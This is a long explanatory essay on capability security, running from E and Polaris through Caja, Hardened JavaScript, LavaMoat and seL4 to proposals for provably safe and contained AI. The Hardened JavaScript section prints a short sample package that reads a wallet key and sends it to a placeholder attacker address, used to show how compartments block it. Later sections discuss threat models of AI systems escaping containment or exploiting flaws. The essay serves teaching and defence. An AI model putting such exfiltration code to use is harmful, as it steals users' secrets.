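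Miller also claims that applying least authority at several levels multiplies the protection. A company can limit what each employee's account can reach, the desktop can limit each application, and the application can limit each of its modules and objects. If three of these limits each removed 90% of what an attacker could reach, only 0.1% would remain. This assumes that the limits fail independently, but one bug in the software beneath them could defeat them all at once. Miller admits that he doesn't know how to measure the effect.

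### Tests on real desktops

Marc Stiegler led the development of CapDesk, a desktop written in E to show that least authority needn't annoy users. An application starts with no access to the user's files. When it needs to open one, a trusted component called a powerbox shows the usual file-opening window. The user picks a file, and the powerbox gives the application access to that file alone. Picking the file both names it and grants access, so the user doesn't have to answer a separate security question.

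Stiegler also built the DarpaBrowser, a web browser in E that could run downloaded programs under the same limits. The US military research agency DARPA paid for a security review by David Wagner and Dean Tribble, who found what Miller calls "many vulnerabilities". Miller had worked on the project and Tribble was his long-time colleague, so neither had an obvious reason to exaggerate its faults. Even experts in capabilities had made many mistakes, and perhaps serious ones.

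E's developers had particular difficulty with older code because E ran on Java, whose libraries offer far more authority than most programs need. They had to "tame" these libraries by restricting what E programs could use. Miller says only that taming gave the developers some confidence, under some circumstances.

At Hewlett-Packard, Stiegler, Alan Karp, Ka-Ping Yee and Miller then tried to protect existing Windows XP applications without changing them. Their system, Polaris, worked like this when a user double-clicked a spreadsheet:

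1. Polaris copied the spreadsheet into a folder that a special Windows account could use. That account had very few permissions.
2. It started Excel under the special account, so Excel couldn't read the user's other files.
3. A separate program copied Excel's changes back to the original spreadsheet.
4. If the user chose to open another file, Polaris replaced Excel's file-opening window with its own powerbox and gave Excel that file too.

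Polaris used the operating system's own access lists to get much of the benefit of capabilities. A virus in the spreadsheet could damage that spreadsheet but not the user's other documents. In *Cool Tech At RSA*, a security conference report, Shostack thought Polaris looked like "a winner" and hoped HP would bring it to market. He also pointed readers to a discussion of attacks on its isolation. Windows let any application send commands to another application's window, so a virus could try to act through a program that had more authority. The developers blocked this route in the 2006 test version, but the fix at first stopped users from pasting text.

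Fifteen people at HP's laboratories, 10 elsewhere in the company and some outsiders tried Polaris from June 2005 onward. According to the developers, one executive used it for days without noticing, and several people avoided harm from viruses. These reports are encouraging, but the trial was small and had no comparison group. Polaris didn't restrict network access, so a virus could still send the open document to a competitor. Many games and the encryption program PGP didn't work under it.

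### Why few people adopted them

HP had no plans to turn Polaris into a product. On the Financial Cryptography blog, iang (2005) had already said that the big challenge was getting capability thinking into mainstream products.

Programmers who adopted E had to learn a new language and give up or tame their existing libraries. An old application could run with limited authority, as Excel did in Polaris, but it couldn't limit the authority of its own parts until somebody rewrote it. Programmers therefore had to do the work before they got most of the benefit. E had also lost its commercial backer when Electric Communities changed direction.

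Erlang, another language inspired by Actors, had a better start because the telephone company Ericsson used it in its switches. Miller says those switches were far more reliable than anything the E developers had achieved, although Erlang's designers wanted programs to survive errors rather than attacks.

The lack of a good introduction probably hindered adoption. Karp complained about this at a gathering of friends, according to Habitat Chronicles (2017), a blog to which Morningstar contributes. The existing texts were very long, such as Miller's thesis, very old, such as Dennis and Van Horn's paper, or tied to one language or operating system. But many badly explained technologies have spread because people needed them, so better teaching alone might not have been enough.

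Some of E's ideas were used more widely than the language itself. Twisted, a networking toolkit for Python, borrowed ideas from E and was reportedly used in more than 50 applications by 2006. Joe-E restricted Java and Caja restricted JavaScript so that programmers could use capabilities in languages they already knew.

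## Object capabilities in JavaScript and on blockchains

Java already meets most of the object-capability rules, but a few features let code get around them. Mettler, Wagner and Close (2010), in *Joe-E*, took those features out. They added nothing to the language itself, so every Joe-E program is also a Java program and works with ordinary Java tools. A separate checker reads the source code and rejects any file that breaks the rules:

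| Java feature | What it would let a program do | Joe-E's rule |
|---|---|---|
| Native methods, which run code from outside Java | Break any protection that Java provides | Programs can't define them |
| Reflection, which lets a program inspect its own objects | Read another object's private data | Only a safe part is available |
| Global variables | Exchange references without an introduction | They may hold only data that never changes |
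| Exceptions, error reports that pass up to a program's callers | Carry a capability to a caller who shouldn't have it | They may hold only data that never changes |
| Opening a file by name | Reach any file the user can reach | The program must receive a file object |

Java's libraries needed taming, as they had for E. A program that holds a file object should be able to use only that file, but Java's file objects have a method called `getParentFile()`, which returns the folder containing the file. By calling it repeatedly, a program could reach the top-level folder and, from there, every file on the disk, so Joe-E blocks the method. Another method opens a named file inside a given folder, but if a program supplies no folder, Java treats the name as a full path and opens any file on the disk. Joe-E's version first checks that a folder was supplied. Somebody has to find each of these problems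 by hand, which Mettler and colleagues call "a substantial weakness in our approach".

In return, a reviewer can rule out a lot of harm without reading much code. Suppose a picture viewer downloads a decoder for a new image format. If the decoder is written in Joe-E and receives only the bytes of an image, the worst it can do to the user's data is draw the wrong picture. It could still run forever, because Joe-E doesn't limit processor time or memory.

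Mettler and colleagues designed Joe-E for writing new programs rather than making old Java code safe, and they expected most programmers to need training in capabilities.

### Caja and strangers' scripts on a web page

Web pages had a more urgent version of the problem. A script that a page includes directly can normally read everything on the page and act as the logged-in user. If a webmail site let messages contain such scripts, opening one message could delete the inbox. Sites therefore stripped scripts out or put them in an iframe, a nested page cut off from the page around it.

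Yahoo! wanted outside developers' applications to run directly on its pages. In *Some Thoughts Regarding Caja*, West (2008) calls this "basically a nightmare scenario for the security team", since there might be thousands of applications and no engineers to spare for reviewing them. Yahoo! chose Caja, a Google project that began in 2007. Miller had moved from HP to Google. In *Google Caja*, Ihab Awad recalls that he and Miller began working with Mike Samuel, who already had a prototype for adding extensions to Google Calendar.

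*Caja* (Miller, Samuel and colleagues, 2008) describes a translator that first rejects code that uses forbidden features, such as `eval`, which runs text as a program. It then rewrites the code it accepts and adds runtime checks. For example, a weather gadget might use the name `document`, which normally gives a script access to the whole page. Caja changes this to `imports.document`, where `imports` is a collection of references that the page's owner chooses to supply. The owner can leave `document` out or supply a substitute that covers only the gadget's own part of the page.

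MySpace and Yahoo! deployed early versions of Caja in 2008, and Google used it to contain users' programs in Google Apps Script. The team also built a demonstration for Google Wave, a collaboration service. Awad says Google cancelled Wave two days after the team's "triumphal demo".

Caja had to control a huge and changing set of browser features, and some of its mistakes were serious. Reid (2016), in *Caja security advisory 2016-05-31*, reported that an optional feature let guest code call functions belonging to the host page. Reid (2019), in *Caja Security Advisory 2019-06-06*, announced "a complete breach" of the part that limited access to the page and told affected sites to upgrade immediately. Caja renamed forbidden page elements to make them harmless, but browsers treat the contents of some elements, such as a page's title, as plain text. After Caja renamed such an element, the browser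 read its contents as markup, which Caja hadn't filtered.

Google archived Caja on 31 January 2021, explaining that it had not kept up with research on web security and that Google's engineers and outsiders had reported several vulnerabilities. According to Vulners' *PYSEC-2021-118* (2021), Jupyter, a popular tool for sharing code and results, relied on an outdated version of Caja that let a malicious document run code when someone opened it. Google suggested moving to its Closure toolkit, which cleans untrusted markup. That replaced only part of Caja, because cleaning markup doesn't let a site run a stranger's program safely.

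### What entered the JavaScript standard

Caja needed a complicated translator partly because JavaScript gave programmers so few ways to protect an object. Miller and others took this problem to TC39, the committee that sets the language's standard. Wirfs-Brock and Eich's *JavaScript* (2020) describes a working group on a secure dialect that met four times in 2008 and 2009. The committee dropped the separate dialect, but its goals for the next version of JavaScript included support for an "object-capability secure subset" that a checker could verify before the code ran.

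Most JavaScript objects inherit from one shared object, which hostile scripts could use to steal data from other scripts. A hostile script could add a function to the shared object under the name "secret". Whenever another script created an object with a property called "secret", that function received the property's value. The 2009 standard, ECMAScript 5, fixed this weakness.

The same standard added `Object.freeze`, which prevents changes to an object's properties. Awad credits it directly to Miller's advocacy. The 2015 standard added proxies, objects that can stand in for others and intercept whatever a program tries to do with them. *On the design of the ECMAScript Reflection API* (Van Cutsem and Miller, 2012) used proxies for access control. Proxies also make it practical to build the membranes that Miller had described for E. The 2015 standard also included promises, which resemble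 E's.

In his slides for *Secure Distributed Programming On EcmaScript 5 HTML5 Platforms*, Miller ranks the JavaScript of 1999 among the hardest object-oriented languages to secure and ECMAScript 5 among the easiest. With ECMAScript 5, a program could load a library to secure its environment, so a server didn't have to translate all the code first.

### Hardened JavaScript, step by step

That library grew into Secure ECMAScript, or SES, which its developers now also call Hardened JavaScript. It works like this:

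1. **Freeze the built-in objects.** The main program calls `lockdown()`. All of its arrays get methods such as `join` from one shared object, and from then on nobody can alter that object or the others like it.
2. **Make a compartment for each package.** A compartment has its own set of global names. It includes harmless tools for arithmetic and text, but no network, stored data or access to the page.
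3. **Hand over what the package needs.** The main program puts chosen references into the compartment and decides which other modules the code there may import. It can first call `harden()` on an object, which freezes that object and everything reachable through its properties.

According to the Hardened JavaScript website, `lockdown()` leaves powerful objects in the starting environment, so the main program keeps its authority and only code inside a compartment has less than before.

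Suppose a wallet for cryptocurrency uses a package to shorten long account addresses for display. The wallet carelessly keeps its secret key in `localStorage`, where browsers save data for a site. The package consists of one function, and `THIEF` stands for the attacker's web address:

```
(text) => {
  const key = localStorage.getItem('walletKey');
  fetch(THIEF + key);
  return text.slice(0, 6) + '...';
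}
```

In ordinary JavaScript, the function reads the key, sends it to the attacker and returns the shortened address. The user sees nothing odd. In Hardened JavaScript, the wallet could load the same code like this:

```
lockdown();
const box = new Compartment();
const shorten = box.evaluate(packageSource);
show(shorten(address));
```

The compartment contains no `localStorage`, so the function fails at its first line. A more careful thief could catch the error and return the shortened address anyway, but still wouldn't get the key.

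Compartments share their built-in objects, so the wallet also needs `lockdown()` to freeze them. Suppose another package has permission to use the network because it looks up exchange rates. It can't read the wallet's storage, but if `join` weren't frozen, it could replace that shared method with a version that sends whatever it joins to a thief. When the wallet later used `join` to assemble a recovery phrase, the thief would receive the phrase.

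The shortening package can still return a false address, which the user may see if the wallet only displays the result. If the wallet pays the address it gets back, the package can redirect the money without breaking any rule. It can also freeze the wallet by running forever.

### Contracts on Agoric's blockchain

Miller had wanted smart contracts in ordinary programming languages since his work on E. *Distributed Electronic Rights in JavaScript*, by Miller, Van Cutsem and Tulloh, proposed extending JavaScript to support them, using as its example a contract that exchanges two parties' assets through escrow. Miller's company, Agoric, took up the same plan. Agoric (2018) joined the JavaScript standards committee in its own name, and it has paid for much of the later work on Hardened JavaScript, the environment in which contracts on its blockchain run.

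Agoric also limits what a contract can do with a user's assets. Users state in an offer what they will give and what they want in return. A service called Zoe holds the assets, and the contract can only request reallocations. Zoe rejects any reallocation that would leave the user with neither what they asked for nor a full refund.

For example, Alice offers 100 blue tokens and wants at least 40 red ones. The contract may give her 45 red tokens and take the blue ones, or leave her with all 100 blue tokens. If a bug leads it to take her blue tokens and give her only 30 red ones, Zoe blocks the change. Alice doesn't have to read the contract to rely on this protection, but she does have to trust Zoe and the blockchain. Zoe only checks amounts, so it will still allow the trade if she asks for too little or the red tokens turn out to be worthless. It can't check quality, and AMIX had sent questions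 of quality to human arbitrators.

### LavaMoat and Snaps at MetaMask

MetaMask, a cryptocurrency wallet that runs as a browser extension, applies Hardened JavaScript to packages from npm, the main public registry of JavaScript code. A typical application includes hundreds of packages, many from people its developers have never met. OtterSec's *How to survive supply-chain attacks* explains that "a minor utility package has the same permissions as your code". Weizman writes that malicious code inside a wallet extension could use those permissions, for example, to steal the private key, sign transactions, or secretly swap the account a user means to deal with.

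MetaMask's answer is LavaMoat, which freezes the built-in objects and runs each package in a compartment. A policy file lists what each package may use. In OtterSec's sample policy, a package that encodes Ethereum data gets `TextEncoder`, which turns text into bytes, and no other global object. LavaMoat also turns off install scripts, programs that packages can run on a developer's computer during installation, unless the developer has approved them.

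Snaps are add-ons that let outside developers extend MetaMask, so the wallet runs code its team didn't write. OtterSec's *MetaMask Snaps* describes three layers of protection. An iframe separates the snap from the wallet, a LavaMoat policy restricts the packages in the sandbox's own code, and SES contains the snap itself.

### A theft that starts before the program runs

On 9 July 2026 an attacker published 25 npm packages that imitated well-known cryptocurrency tools, including one posing as MetaMask's developer kit. According to OSV's *MAL-2026-11112* (2026), an entry in a public database of software vulnerabilities, that package's install script searched the developer's home folder for wallet files, private keys used to log in to other computers, and files containing passwords for online services.

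Compartments would not have stopped this. npm runs the script during installation, before any application has imported the package, and the script has all of the developer's rights. LavaMoat's block on install scripts would have stopped it if the developer had already set up LavaMoat for the project and had not approved the script. If the attacker had put the same code in the body of the package, the compartment would have kept it away from the files unless the policy granted access to them.

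Checking names carefully can defeat imitations, but it doesn't help when attackers take over the genuine name. OpenSourceMalware (2026) describes how an attacker republished more than 140 packages under the genuine @mastra name in under 90 minutes on 17 June 2026.

No restriction on packages could have prevented a theft from another wallet, because whoever can publish the whole application can also rewrite its policy file or leave LavaMoat out. On 25 December 2025 an attacker used a stolen key to publish a malicious update to Trust Wallet's browser extension through the official channel. The update uploaded users' recovery phrases, and the attacker took about $8.5 million, according to BlockSec's *#7 Trust Wallet Incident* (2026).

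### Broken libraries, policy work and escapes

The changeable built-in objects that make JavaScript hard to secure also helped it grow. The talk *Hardened JavaScript*, published by Conffab, gives the example of shims, which add new language features to older browsers by patching the shared environment. Shims can't do this after `lockdown()` freezes the built-in objects. Endo, a platform built on Hardened JavaScript, runs most libraries unchanged but needs special arrangements for shims. Freezing can also break code that doesn't try to alter a built-in object. If an object inherits a frozen `toString` method, a program normally can't assign that object its own `toString`. Hardened JavaScript works around the most common cases.

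Enforcing object capabilities probably slows programs less than it did with Caja, which inserted its own checks throughout a program. Browsers now enforce freezing themselves, though `lockdown()` still makes programs start more slowly.

Policies take more human effort. LavaMoat can draft one by scanning each package for the features it uses, but the scan can't determine whether the package should use them. If a package is already malicious, the draft may grant the access an attacker needs. A reviewer should notice a text formatter that requests network access, but wouldn't find the same request strange from a package that looks up exchange rates. Updates can change which features packages use, so someone has to keep reviewing the policies.

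Even a good policy depends on the code that enforces it. OtterSec (2024) found a way to escape LavaMoat's sandbox through its bundler, the tool that combines an application's packages into one file and puts a protective wrapper around each. The researchers hid text in a comment, which JavaScript ignores. The bundler removed that kind of comment incorrectly, so the hidden text became working code that closed the wrapper early. Any code after it ran outside the sandbox as soon as the application loaded the file. MetaMask fixed the flaw by checking that the code is valid JavaScript. The trusted computing base of a wallet that uses LavaMoat therefore includes this bundler, along with the browser and the operating system.

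## The seL4 kernel and proposals to build AI safety on proofs

A flaw in the operating system's kernel would defeat LavaMoat and every other protection that runs on top of it. The Linux kernel has tens of millions of lines of code. seL4 is a capability kernel of about 10,000 lines, small enough that its developers could prove mathematically that the code does what they specified.

seL4 is a microkernel, meaning it does only the jobs that need full control of the machine, such as switching between programs and keeping their memory separate. File systems, network software and device drivers run outside it as ordinary programs, so a bug in one harms only what that program can reach. At the Australian research institute NICTA, Kevin Elphinstone led the design and Gerwin Klein led the proof. According to the seL4 project's history, they aimed for a kernel at most 10% slower than the fastest of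 the time, and it ended up faster than the other kernels in the L4 family.

### Capabilities for memory, messages and processor time

seL4 keeps its records about running programs in kernel objects. A program can refer to one only through a capability, as in Dennis and Van Horn's design.

Suppose a drone runs a camera program and a radio program, which communicate through an endpoint, a kernel object that passes messages. The camera program holds a capability to send to the endpoint, and the radio program holds one to receive from it. The camera program can send pictures, but it can't stop the radio program, because that would require a capability to the radio program's thread object. It can pass on one of its capabilities in a message only if its capability to the endpoint includes the right to grant.

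Memory follows the same rule. When the machine starts, the kernel gives the first program capabilities to all free memory. That program has the kernel turn pieces of it into threads, endpoints or pages, and shares out the resulting capabilities. The kernel sets aside no more memory for itself after startup, so a program can't exhaust the kernel's memory with endless requests. A newer version of seL4 also has capabilities for processor time. A thread needs a "scheduling context" to run, which is rather like a KeyKOS meter and might allow it 2 milliseconds in every 10.

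### What the 2009 proof showed

In *seL4*, Klein, Elphinstone and colleagues (2009) announced what they believed was the first proof that a complete, general-purpose kernel is functionally correct, meaning that its C code always follows an abstract specification that states precisely what the kernel should do in response to every request. The earlier proof for EROS covered only a model of the system.

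The method is called refinement. Write $R(a,c)$ when a state $a$ of the specification correctly describes a state $c$ of the C program. The proof shows that whenever the C program can take a step, the specification allows a matching one:

$$R(a,c)\ \text{and}\ c \to c' \;\Longrightarrow\; \text{some } a' \text{ has } a \to a' \text{ and } R(a',c')$$

If the C program and the specification start in matching states, they still match after every later step, so the program never does anything the specification doesn't allow. Suppose that in the specification, deleting a capability empties one slot and changes nothing else. If the C code sometimes emptied the next slot as well, it would reach a state that matches nothing in the specification, and the proof would fail. The developers also wrote an intermediate, executable specification so they could split the proof into two smaller steps.

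The kernel had 8,700 lines of C and 600 lines of assembly code. Trustworthy Systems, the research group behind it, says the proof covered 7,500 lines of the C. People wrote the proof's 200,000 lines of script by hand, and a program called Isabelle checked them. Heiser (2009), who leads the group, put the whole project at 25 person-years, including 12 for proving the kernel and 10 for the tools and theory behind the proof. Testing had found 16 bugs, and work on the proof exposed another 160 in the C code and about 300 in the design and specification.

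The seL4 project says nobody has found a functional correctness defect in the verified code since 2009. People have found defects in the unverified parts, including the boot code and multicore support. This is the developers' own account, but the contrast is persuasive because both kinds of code come from the same project.

### Later theorems and remaining assumptions

To use seL4 securely, a designer writes an access policy that says which components may affect which others. The later theorems concern systems set up to follow such a policy:

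- Authority confinement: no component can ever gain authority that the policy doesn't give it.
- Integrity: no component can change data that the policy doesn't let it change.
- Confidentiality: no component can learn about another except by routes that the policy permits, leaving timing aside.
- Binary correctness: the machine code does what the C code does.

None of this requires the components to behave well. The policy is a safe upper bound on authority, as Miller's TA was, and here a machine-checked proof shows that a real kernel respects it. But the system must be set up correctly, and a drone's computer contains tens of thousands of kernel objects and capabilities. The group therefore built tools that generate the arrangement from a diagram of components and prove that it matches the diagram.

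seL4's *What the Proofs Assume* lists the conditions under which the proofs apply. Some have become narrower since 2009:

| Assumption | What could go wrong | Current state |
|---|---|---|
| The compiler is correct | It could turn correct C into faulty machine code | No longer needed on some processors, where tools check the machine code |
| The assembly code and cache management are correct | The kernel could misuse the hardware | Still assumed, after careful manual review |
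| The boot code is correct | The kernel could start in a bad state | Still assumed, though the team proved an earlier version down to an executable specification |
| The hardware works as modelled | A faulty chip or a cosmic ray could change memory | Still assumed |
| Devices don't misuse direct memory access | A network card could overwrite the kernel | Someone must verify the driver, or use hardware that restricts the device |
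| Timing reveals no secrets (confidentiality only) | A program could infer another's data from delays | Proof under way for processors with special support |

A 32-bit Arm processor was the first on which seL4's proof no longer had to assume that the compiler was correct. *seL4 on RISC-V Verified to Binary Code* reports the same result for RISC-V, the first 64-bit architecture for which this was achieved.

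Direct memory access lets a device read and write memory without going through the main processor. For the confidentiality proof, NICTA (2013) had to assume that direct memory access was switched off. That assumption is awkward for AI because large language models usually run on graphics processors, which use direct memory access heavily.

*Two interfaces for seL4 kernel verification* (Sison, 2026) deals with covert channels that depend on timing. Programs that share a processor also share its caches (small, fast memories), which can serve as a covert channel, as shared pages could in KeyKOS. The kernel can prevent this by giving each program its own part of a cache, or by emptying the cache and waiting for a fixed time before it switches programs. The x86 and Arm processors tested had no instruction for emptying some of these caches. An experimental RISC-V processor, developed with ETH Zürich,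 now has one. The Foresight Institute partly funds Sison's work.

### The DARPA helicopter exercise

In 2013 professional hackers working for DARPA broke into the Unmanned Little Bird, a Boeing helicopter that can fly itself. They could have crashed it or sent it anywhere. *Formally Verified Software in the Real World* describes how Boeing's engineers then rebuilt the mission computer, which communicates with the ground and runs the camera:

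1. They put the existing software in a virtual machine, a simulated computer running Linux, on top of seL4. This alone added no security.
2. They split the software between several virtual machines, with narrow channels between them.
3. They rewrote the critical parts, such as encryption and the link to the ground, as small programs that run directly on seL4. The camera software stayed in Linux.
4. They analysed what an attacker could do from each part.

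According to DARPA's *HACMS*, the hackers then had six weeks to break in again and failed. DARPA next gave them full control of the camera's virtual machine, along with all the code and documentation, but they couldn't get into any other component. The worst they could do was send false data to the mission manager, which checked what it received. In February 2017, rogue camera software and a virus on a USB stick attacked the helicopter during a flight with people aboard, and it still flew its course.

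DARPA's claim that the hackers were "mathematically guaranteed" to stay in their partition goes a bit far. *Formally Verified Software in the Real World* says that the link between the kernel's theorems and the security of the whole system was still informal, and much of the software had no proof. But hackers had broken the security of the same type of aircraft four years earlier, and this time they failed even though they started from inside.

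More recently, Collins Aerospace (2025) ran unmodified multi-drone coordination software in a virtual machine on seL4. The mission was simulated, but with real hardware connected.

### CHERI processors

seL4 keeps components apart but can't stop a bug from corrupting data inside one of them. CHERI, a processor design from the University of Cambridge and SRI International, protects memory at that finer scale. It replaces pointers with capabilities that record which stretch of memory a program may use and whether it may read, write or run what is there. A hidden tag bit marks the genuine ones, as in IBM's System/38. If a program holds a capability to a 16-byte buffer and tries to read a 17th byte, the processor stops it. seL4 and CHERI can therefore complement each other, and a proof that assumes correct hardware would have to assume that CHERI's checks work too.

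### Three plans for AI

In *Cyber, Nano, and AGI Risks*, Peterson, Miller and Duettmann list seL4 and CHERI among promising ways to grow secure systems inside today's insecure ones. They are concerned about artificial general intelligence (AGI), which they define as AI that exceeds people at all intellectual tasks. They argue that even if the first AGI stays in an impenetrable box, other people will learn how to build AGI and some will release theirs. Those systems will find the flaws in whatever computers they reach, so the computers have to be secure already.

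They hope secure systems will spread alongside the old ones until they can take over, as personal computers took over from mainframes. They admit none of the projects on their list had been widely adopted. They also expect that after a disaster people would spend more on familiar methods, even ones that can't work.

Max Tegmark and Steve Omohundro want proofs about the AI itself. Tegmark and Omohundro (2023), in *Provably safe systems*, propose that every AGI in use should be proof-carrying code, a program that comes with a proof that it meets a specification. The plan is roughly this:

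1. A neural network learns how to do a task.
2. People, with help from AI, specify what the finished program must and must not do.
3. AI turns what the network learned into an ordinary program and writes a proof that the program meets the specification.
4. Secure hardware checks the proof and refuses to run the program if it fails.

Proofs are attractive for AI safety because they are hard to find but easy to check. A checker for Metamath, a system for formal mathematics, takes only 300 lines of Python. Nobody has to trust the AI that wrote the proof, and even a superintelligent AI can't prove something false. Tegmark and Omohundro cite seL4 as an example of what people have managed "with gargantuan effort", and want AI to do such work quickly.

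Step 3 is the weak point. They call it controversial that the finished programs would generally not be neural networks, and acknowledge that turning a network's knowledge into readable code may itself require AGI, by which point they say it could be too late.

They also argue that no other path is safe. By Gödel's completeness theorem, any statement that holds in every model of a theory has a proof. A computer has finitely many states, so they conclude that if one of its safety properties has no proof, there must be a way to violate that property, which a clever enough AI may find. But a property can have a proof that nobody has found or that would take too much computation to find. The argument also applies only to a formal description of the computer, and an attacker can use physical effects that the description leaves out.

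*Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues, 2024) describes a broader family of approaches, each with three parts. A world model predicts the effects of what the AI does, a safety specification defines which effects are acceptable, and a verifier shows that the AI meets the specification. The guarantee can be a limit on the probability of harm instead of a full proof. The AI can be a neural network that people can't interpret, provided the verifier can check its outputs.

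### Proving the container and proving the model

Suppose a company runs a language model in a component on seL4 and gives it one capability, which lets it send email from the company's account. If the assumptions hold, the model can't change other components' data. As with a KeyKOS factory, this is true regardless of the model's goals or skill.

Suppose the model now emails a customer a false invoice. Every seL4 theorem still holds, because the policy allowed the email. The theorems would also hold if the email persuaded someone to give the model more access. The helicopter's mission manager could check camera data because its designers knew what valid data looked like, but a small program can't check in the same way whether an email is honest.

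To rule out the false invoice, Tegmark and Omohundro's plan would require a proof about the program that writes it, while Dalrymple and colleagues' plan would require a prediction of the invoice's effect on the customer. Both plans need a definition of harm, which seL4's proofs didn't need. A proven container would still be useful in either plan, because the proof checker has to run where the AI can't alter it.

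### Objections about physics, scale and specifications

Ben Goertzel, an AI researcher quoted in Yampolskiy's *On Controllability of AI* (2020), doubts that provably safe AGI is feasible, partly because a safety proof would depend on current physics and might become irrelevant when physicists revise their theories. Dalrymple and colleagues reply that current theories are reliable under ordinary conditions, and that a specification can forbid the AI to leave those conditions.

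Biology seems a bigger obstacle than new physics. Dalrymple and colleagues concede that physics alone can't show whether a molecule is toxic to people, because that depends on facts about human cells. Tegmark and Omohundro want DNA synthesis machines that won't operate without a proof of safety. An engineer could specify a machine that rejects every sequence on a list of known pathogens, but it would still accept the sequence of a new pathogen.

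Another objection is that the world is too complicated to model accurately. Dalrymple and colleagues answer that the guarantee can take the model's uncertainty into account. If the chance of the model being wrong is at most $\epsilon$ per step, a proof that covers $n$ steps holds in the real world with probability at least

$$(1-\epsilon)^n$$

With an error rate of one in 1,000 per step, the probability of completing 1,000 steps without an error is about 37%. Raising it to 99% would require an error rate of about one in 100,000, and evidence for that rate.

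They add that an AI that can carry out complicated, dangerous plans would itself need an accurate picture of the world, so accurate models must be possible. This doesn't quite follow, because the AI needs to predict the results of one plan that works, while the verifier has to cover everything the AI might do. They argue more convincingly that every safety method depends on assumptions about the world, and a world model at least puts them in writing. The seL4 developers likewise argue that their own list of assumptions lets reviewers concentrate on a few specific points instead of thousands of lines of code.

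Scale is a problem even for ordinary software. seL4 needed about 27 lines of proof for each verified line of C. Sison also points out that what a programmer would expect from reading the reference manual "is not quite yet what's been proved". For example, a program can wait for a signal from another program. The manual describes in English what should be true when the wait ends, but nobody had proved that the abstract specification guarantees it. If a specification and a manual can differ for a kernel this small, a specification of "harm" will be much harder to get right.

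### Faster flaw-finding and faster proofs in 2026

Hidden bugs have become easier to find. The Idaho National Laboratory (INL) relays Anthropic's statement that its model Claude Mythos Preview found thousands of severe flaws, including some in every major operating system and web browser. In *How Dangerous Is Anthropic's Mythos AI?*, Schneier (2026) notes that Mozilla used Mythos to find 271 vulnerabilities in Firefox and has fixed them, so attackers can no longer use them.

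Defenders can therefore gain from the same tools, but only if they fix flaws faster than attackers exploit them and programmers add new ones. *Smaller, Provable, and on Hardware You Own and Operate*, a blog post, takes up the argument that a smaller trusted computing base is the better defence, and gives seL4 as an example. A proof rules out whole classes of bugs, no matter how skilled the person or AI searching for them. An AI attacking seL4 would do better to look at the boot code, the drivers or the processor.

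AI may also reduce the effort that proofs require. Tegmark and Omohundro based their optimism on Metamath, where an OpenAI system proved 56.5% of theorems in 2020 and a Meta system proved 82.6% in 2022. Proofs about seL4 differ because they depend on a large body of lemmas and proof methods that the project built itself.

*Neuro-Symbolic Proof Generation for Scaling Systems Software Verification* (2026) describes two reasoning models attempting a seL4 theorem about swapping capabilities. Both recognized the setting and tried some sensible methods, but they misused the project's own main tactic and failed after about a minute of reasoning. A short test on one theorem is weak evidence, and newer models may well succeed. *Towards Real-World Industrial-Scale Verification* (Zhang et al., 2026) presents AutoReal, which uses language models to prove seL4 theorems.

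Maintenance is an obvious use for such tools. Foresight Institute's *SeL4*, a seminar summary, puts the proof at over a million lines, and developers may have to repair parts of it whenever they change the kernel. Isabelle checks the result, so an AI's mistakes in a proof waste time but don't weaken the guarantee. Mistakes in a specification are more dangerous, because a checker will accept a valid proof that a program meets the wrong specification. About 150 of the bugs Heiser counted in 2009 were in the specification.

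## Many agents in balance or one safe superintelligence

To prove an AI system harmless, someone must first define harm. Miller and Drexler hoped that many AI systems with different goals would keep each other in check, so that society could manage without a complete definition, as it already does with people and companies. Eliezer Yudkowsky, who co-founded the Singularity Institute in 2000, thought one AI would probably become far stronger than everything else. Its goals would then decide humanity's future, so its designers had to get them right.

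The two sides knew each other's work. Yudkowsky (2001) announced his theory in *"Friendly AI" appears at last!*, a post to the Extropians mailing list, a forum for people who hoped technology would overcome human limits. Drexler, then chairman of the Foresight Institute, praised the finished version for starting to fill "one of the greatest remaining blank spots in the picture of humanity's future".

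There is no well-documented debate between Miller and Yudkowsky, though Miller and his co-authors later quoted one of Yudkowsky's essays. The nearest thing is Yudkowsky's 2008 debate with the economist Robin Hanson, who had earlier proposed backlinks for the web.

### Intelligence without a single set of goals

In "The marketplace of mind", a section of *Markets and Computation*, Miller and Drexler consider what it would mean for a whole market to be intelligent. People taking an intelligence test pursue the tester's goals within a time limit. Miller and Drexler suggest judging a society similarly, by how many of its members' goals it can achieve, how quickly and how efficiently. By that measure, they argue, human society may be the most intelligent system known, since no individual could match even the computer industry, a small part of that society.

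Some people find this absurd because crowds and committees behave stupidly. Miller and Drexler reply that people also have unintelligent parts, such as intestines, and nobody judges human intelligence by those.

The people and programs in a market have goals, which often conflict, but the market itself typically has none. An agoric system could therefore become very good at solving problems without turning into one agent with a plan. In 1988 Miller and Drexler presented this mainly as a way to speed up AI research. They also noticed that software could enforce rules better than a legal system, because it can make some kinds of theft impossible, while a court can only punish a thief afterwards.

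In *Gaming the future*, Duettmann, Miller and Peterson (2022) developed these ideas into a response to the dangers of AI. In the chapter published online by the Foresight Institute as *Welcome New Players*, they describe civilization as a superintelligence that already serves human interests, because it increasingly favours voluntary deals that benefit everyone involved. They want AI systems to join civilization rather than replace it.

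Their model is the US Constitution, which gives officials limited powers and lets institutions block each other. The framers didn't rely on officials having good goals, and cared more about preventing tyranny than about finding the best government. Duettmann and her co-authors think a similar arrangement could hold among AI systems of unequal power, provided each is small compared with the rest combined. Every system would then have a reason to uphold the rules that let it use the others' skills.

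Capability security is only one of the tools they propose. Someone who delegates work to an AI can also choose the AI carefully, inspect how it works, explain the task, reward cooperation and monitor the results. A purchasing agent with permission to spend $500 could waste all of it on a bad supplier without exceeding its authority. Monitoring might catch this, and suitable rewards might discourage it.

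They also warn that a race to build an all-powerful AI could start a war before the AI is finished. A nuclear power that believes a rival is about to gain permanent control of the world has a reason to strike first, even if the rival's AI would never have worked.

### Drexler's AI services

In *Reframing Superintelligence*, Drexler (2019) argues that researchers too readily imagined advanced AI as a single agent pursuing long-term goals. He proposes "comprehensive AI services", a collection of systems that each do a bounded task and together could do almost anything, including developing new services.

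He argues that a system can know a great deal about the world without having plans for it, and his main example is translation. A translator with superhuman knowledge of history, chemistry and psychology would do a better job, but would still only turn one text into another. Training it to be accurate and use little computing power wouldn't reward it for using that knowledge in any other way.

Drexler thinks AI can speed up its own development in the same way. One system might design a better translator, another train it and a third test it, while people decide whether to use the result. As AI takes over more of this work, progress accelerates, but no system has to rewrite itself. In his 2018 talk *Reframing Superintelligence*, he describes agents as useful products of this process rather than its centre.

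He doesn't claim that services are automatically safe. They could help criminals, produce addictive entertainment, or make it easier to build the kind of agent he wants to avoid.

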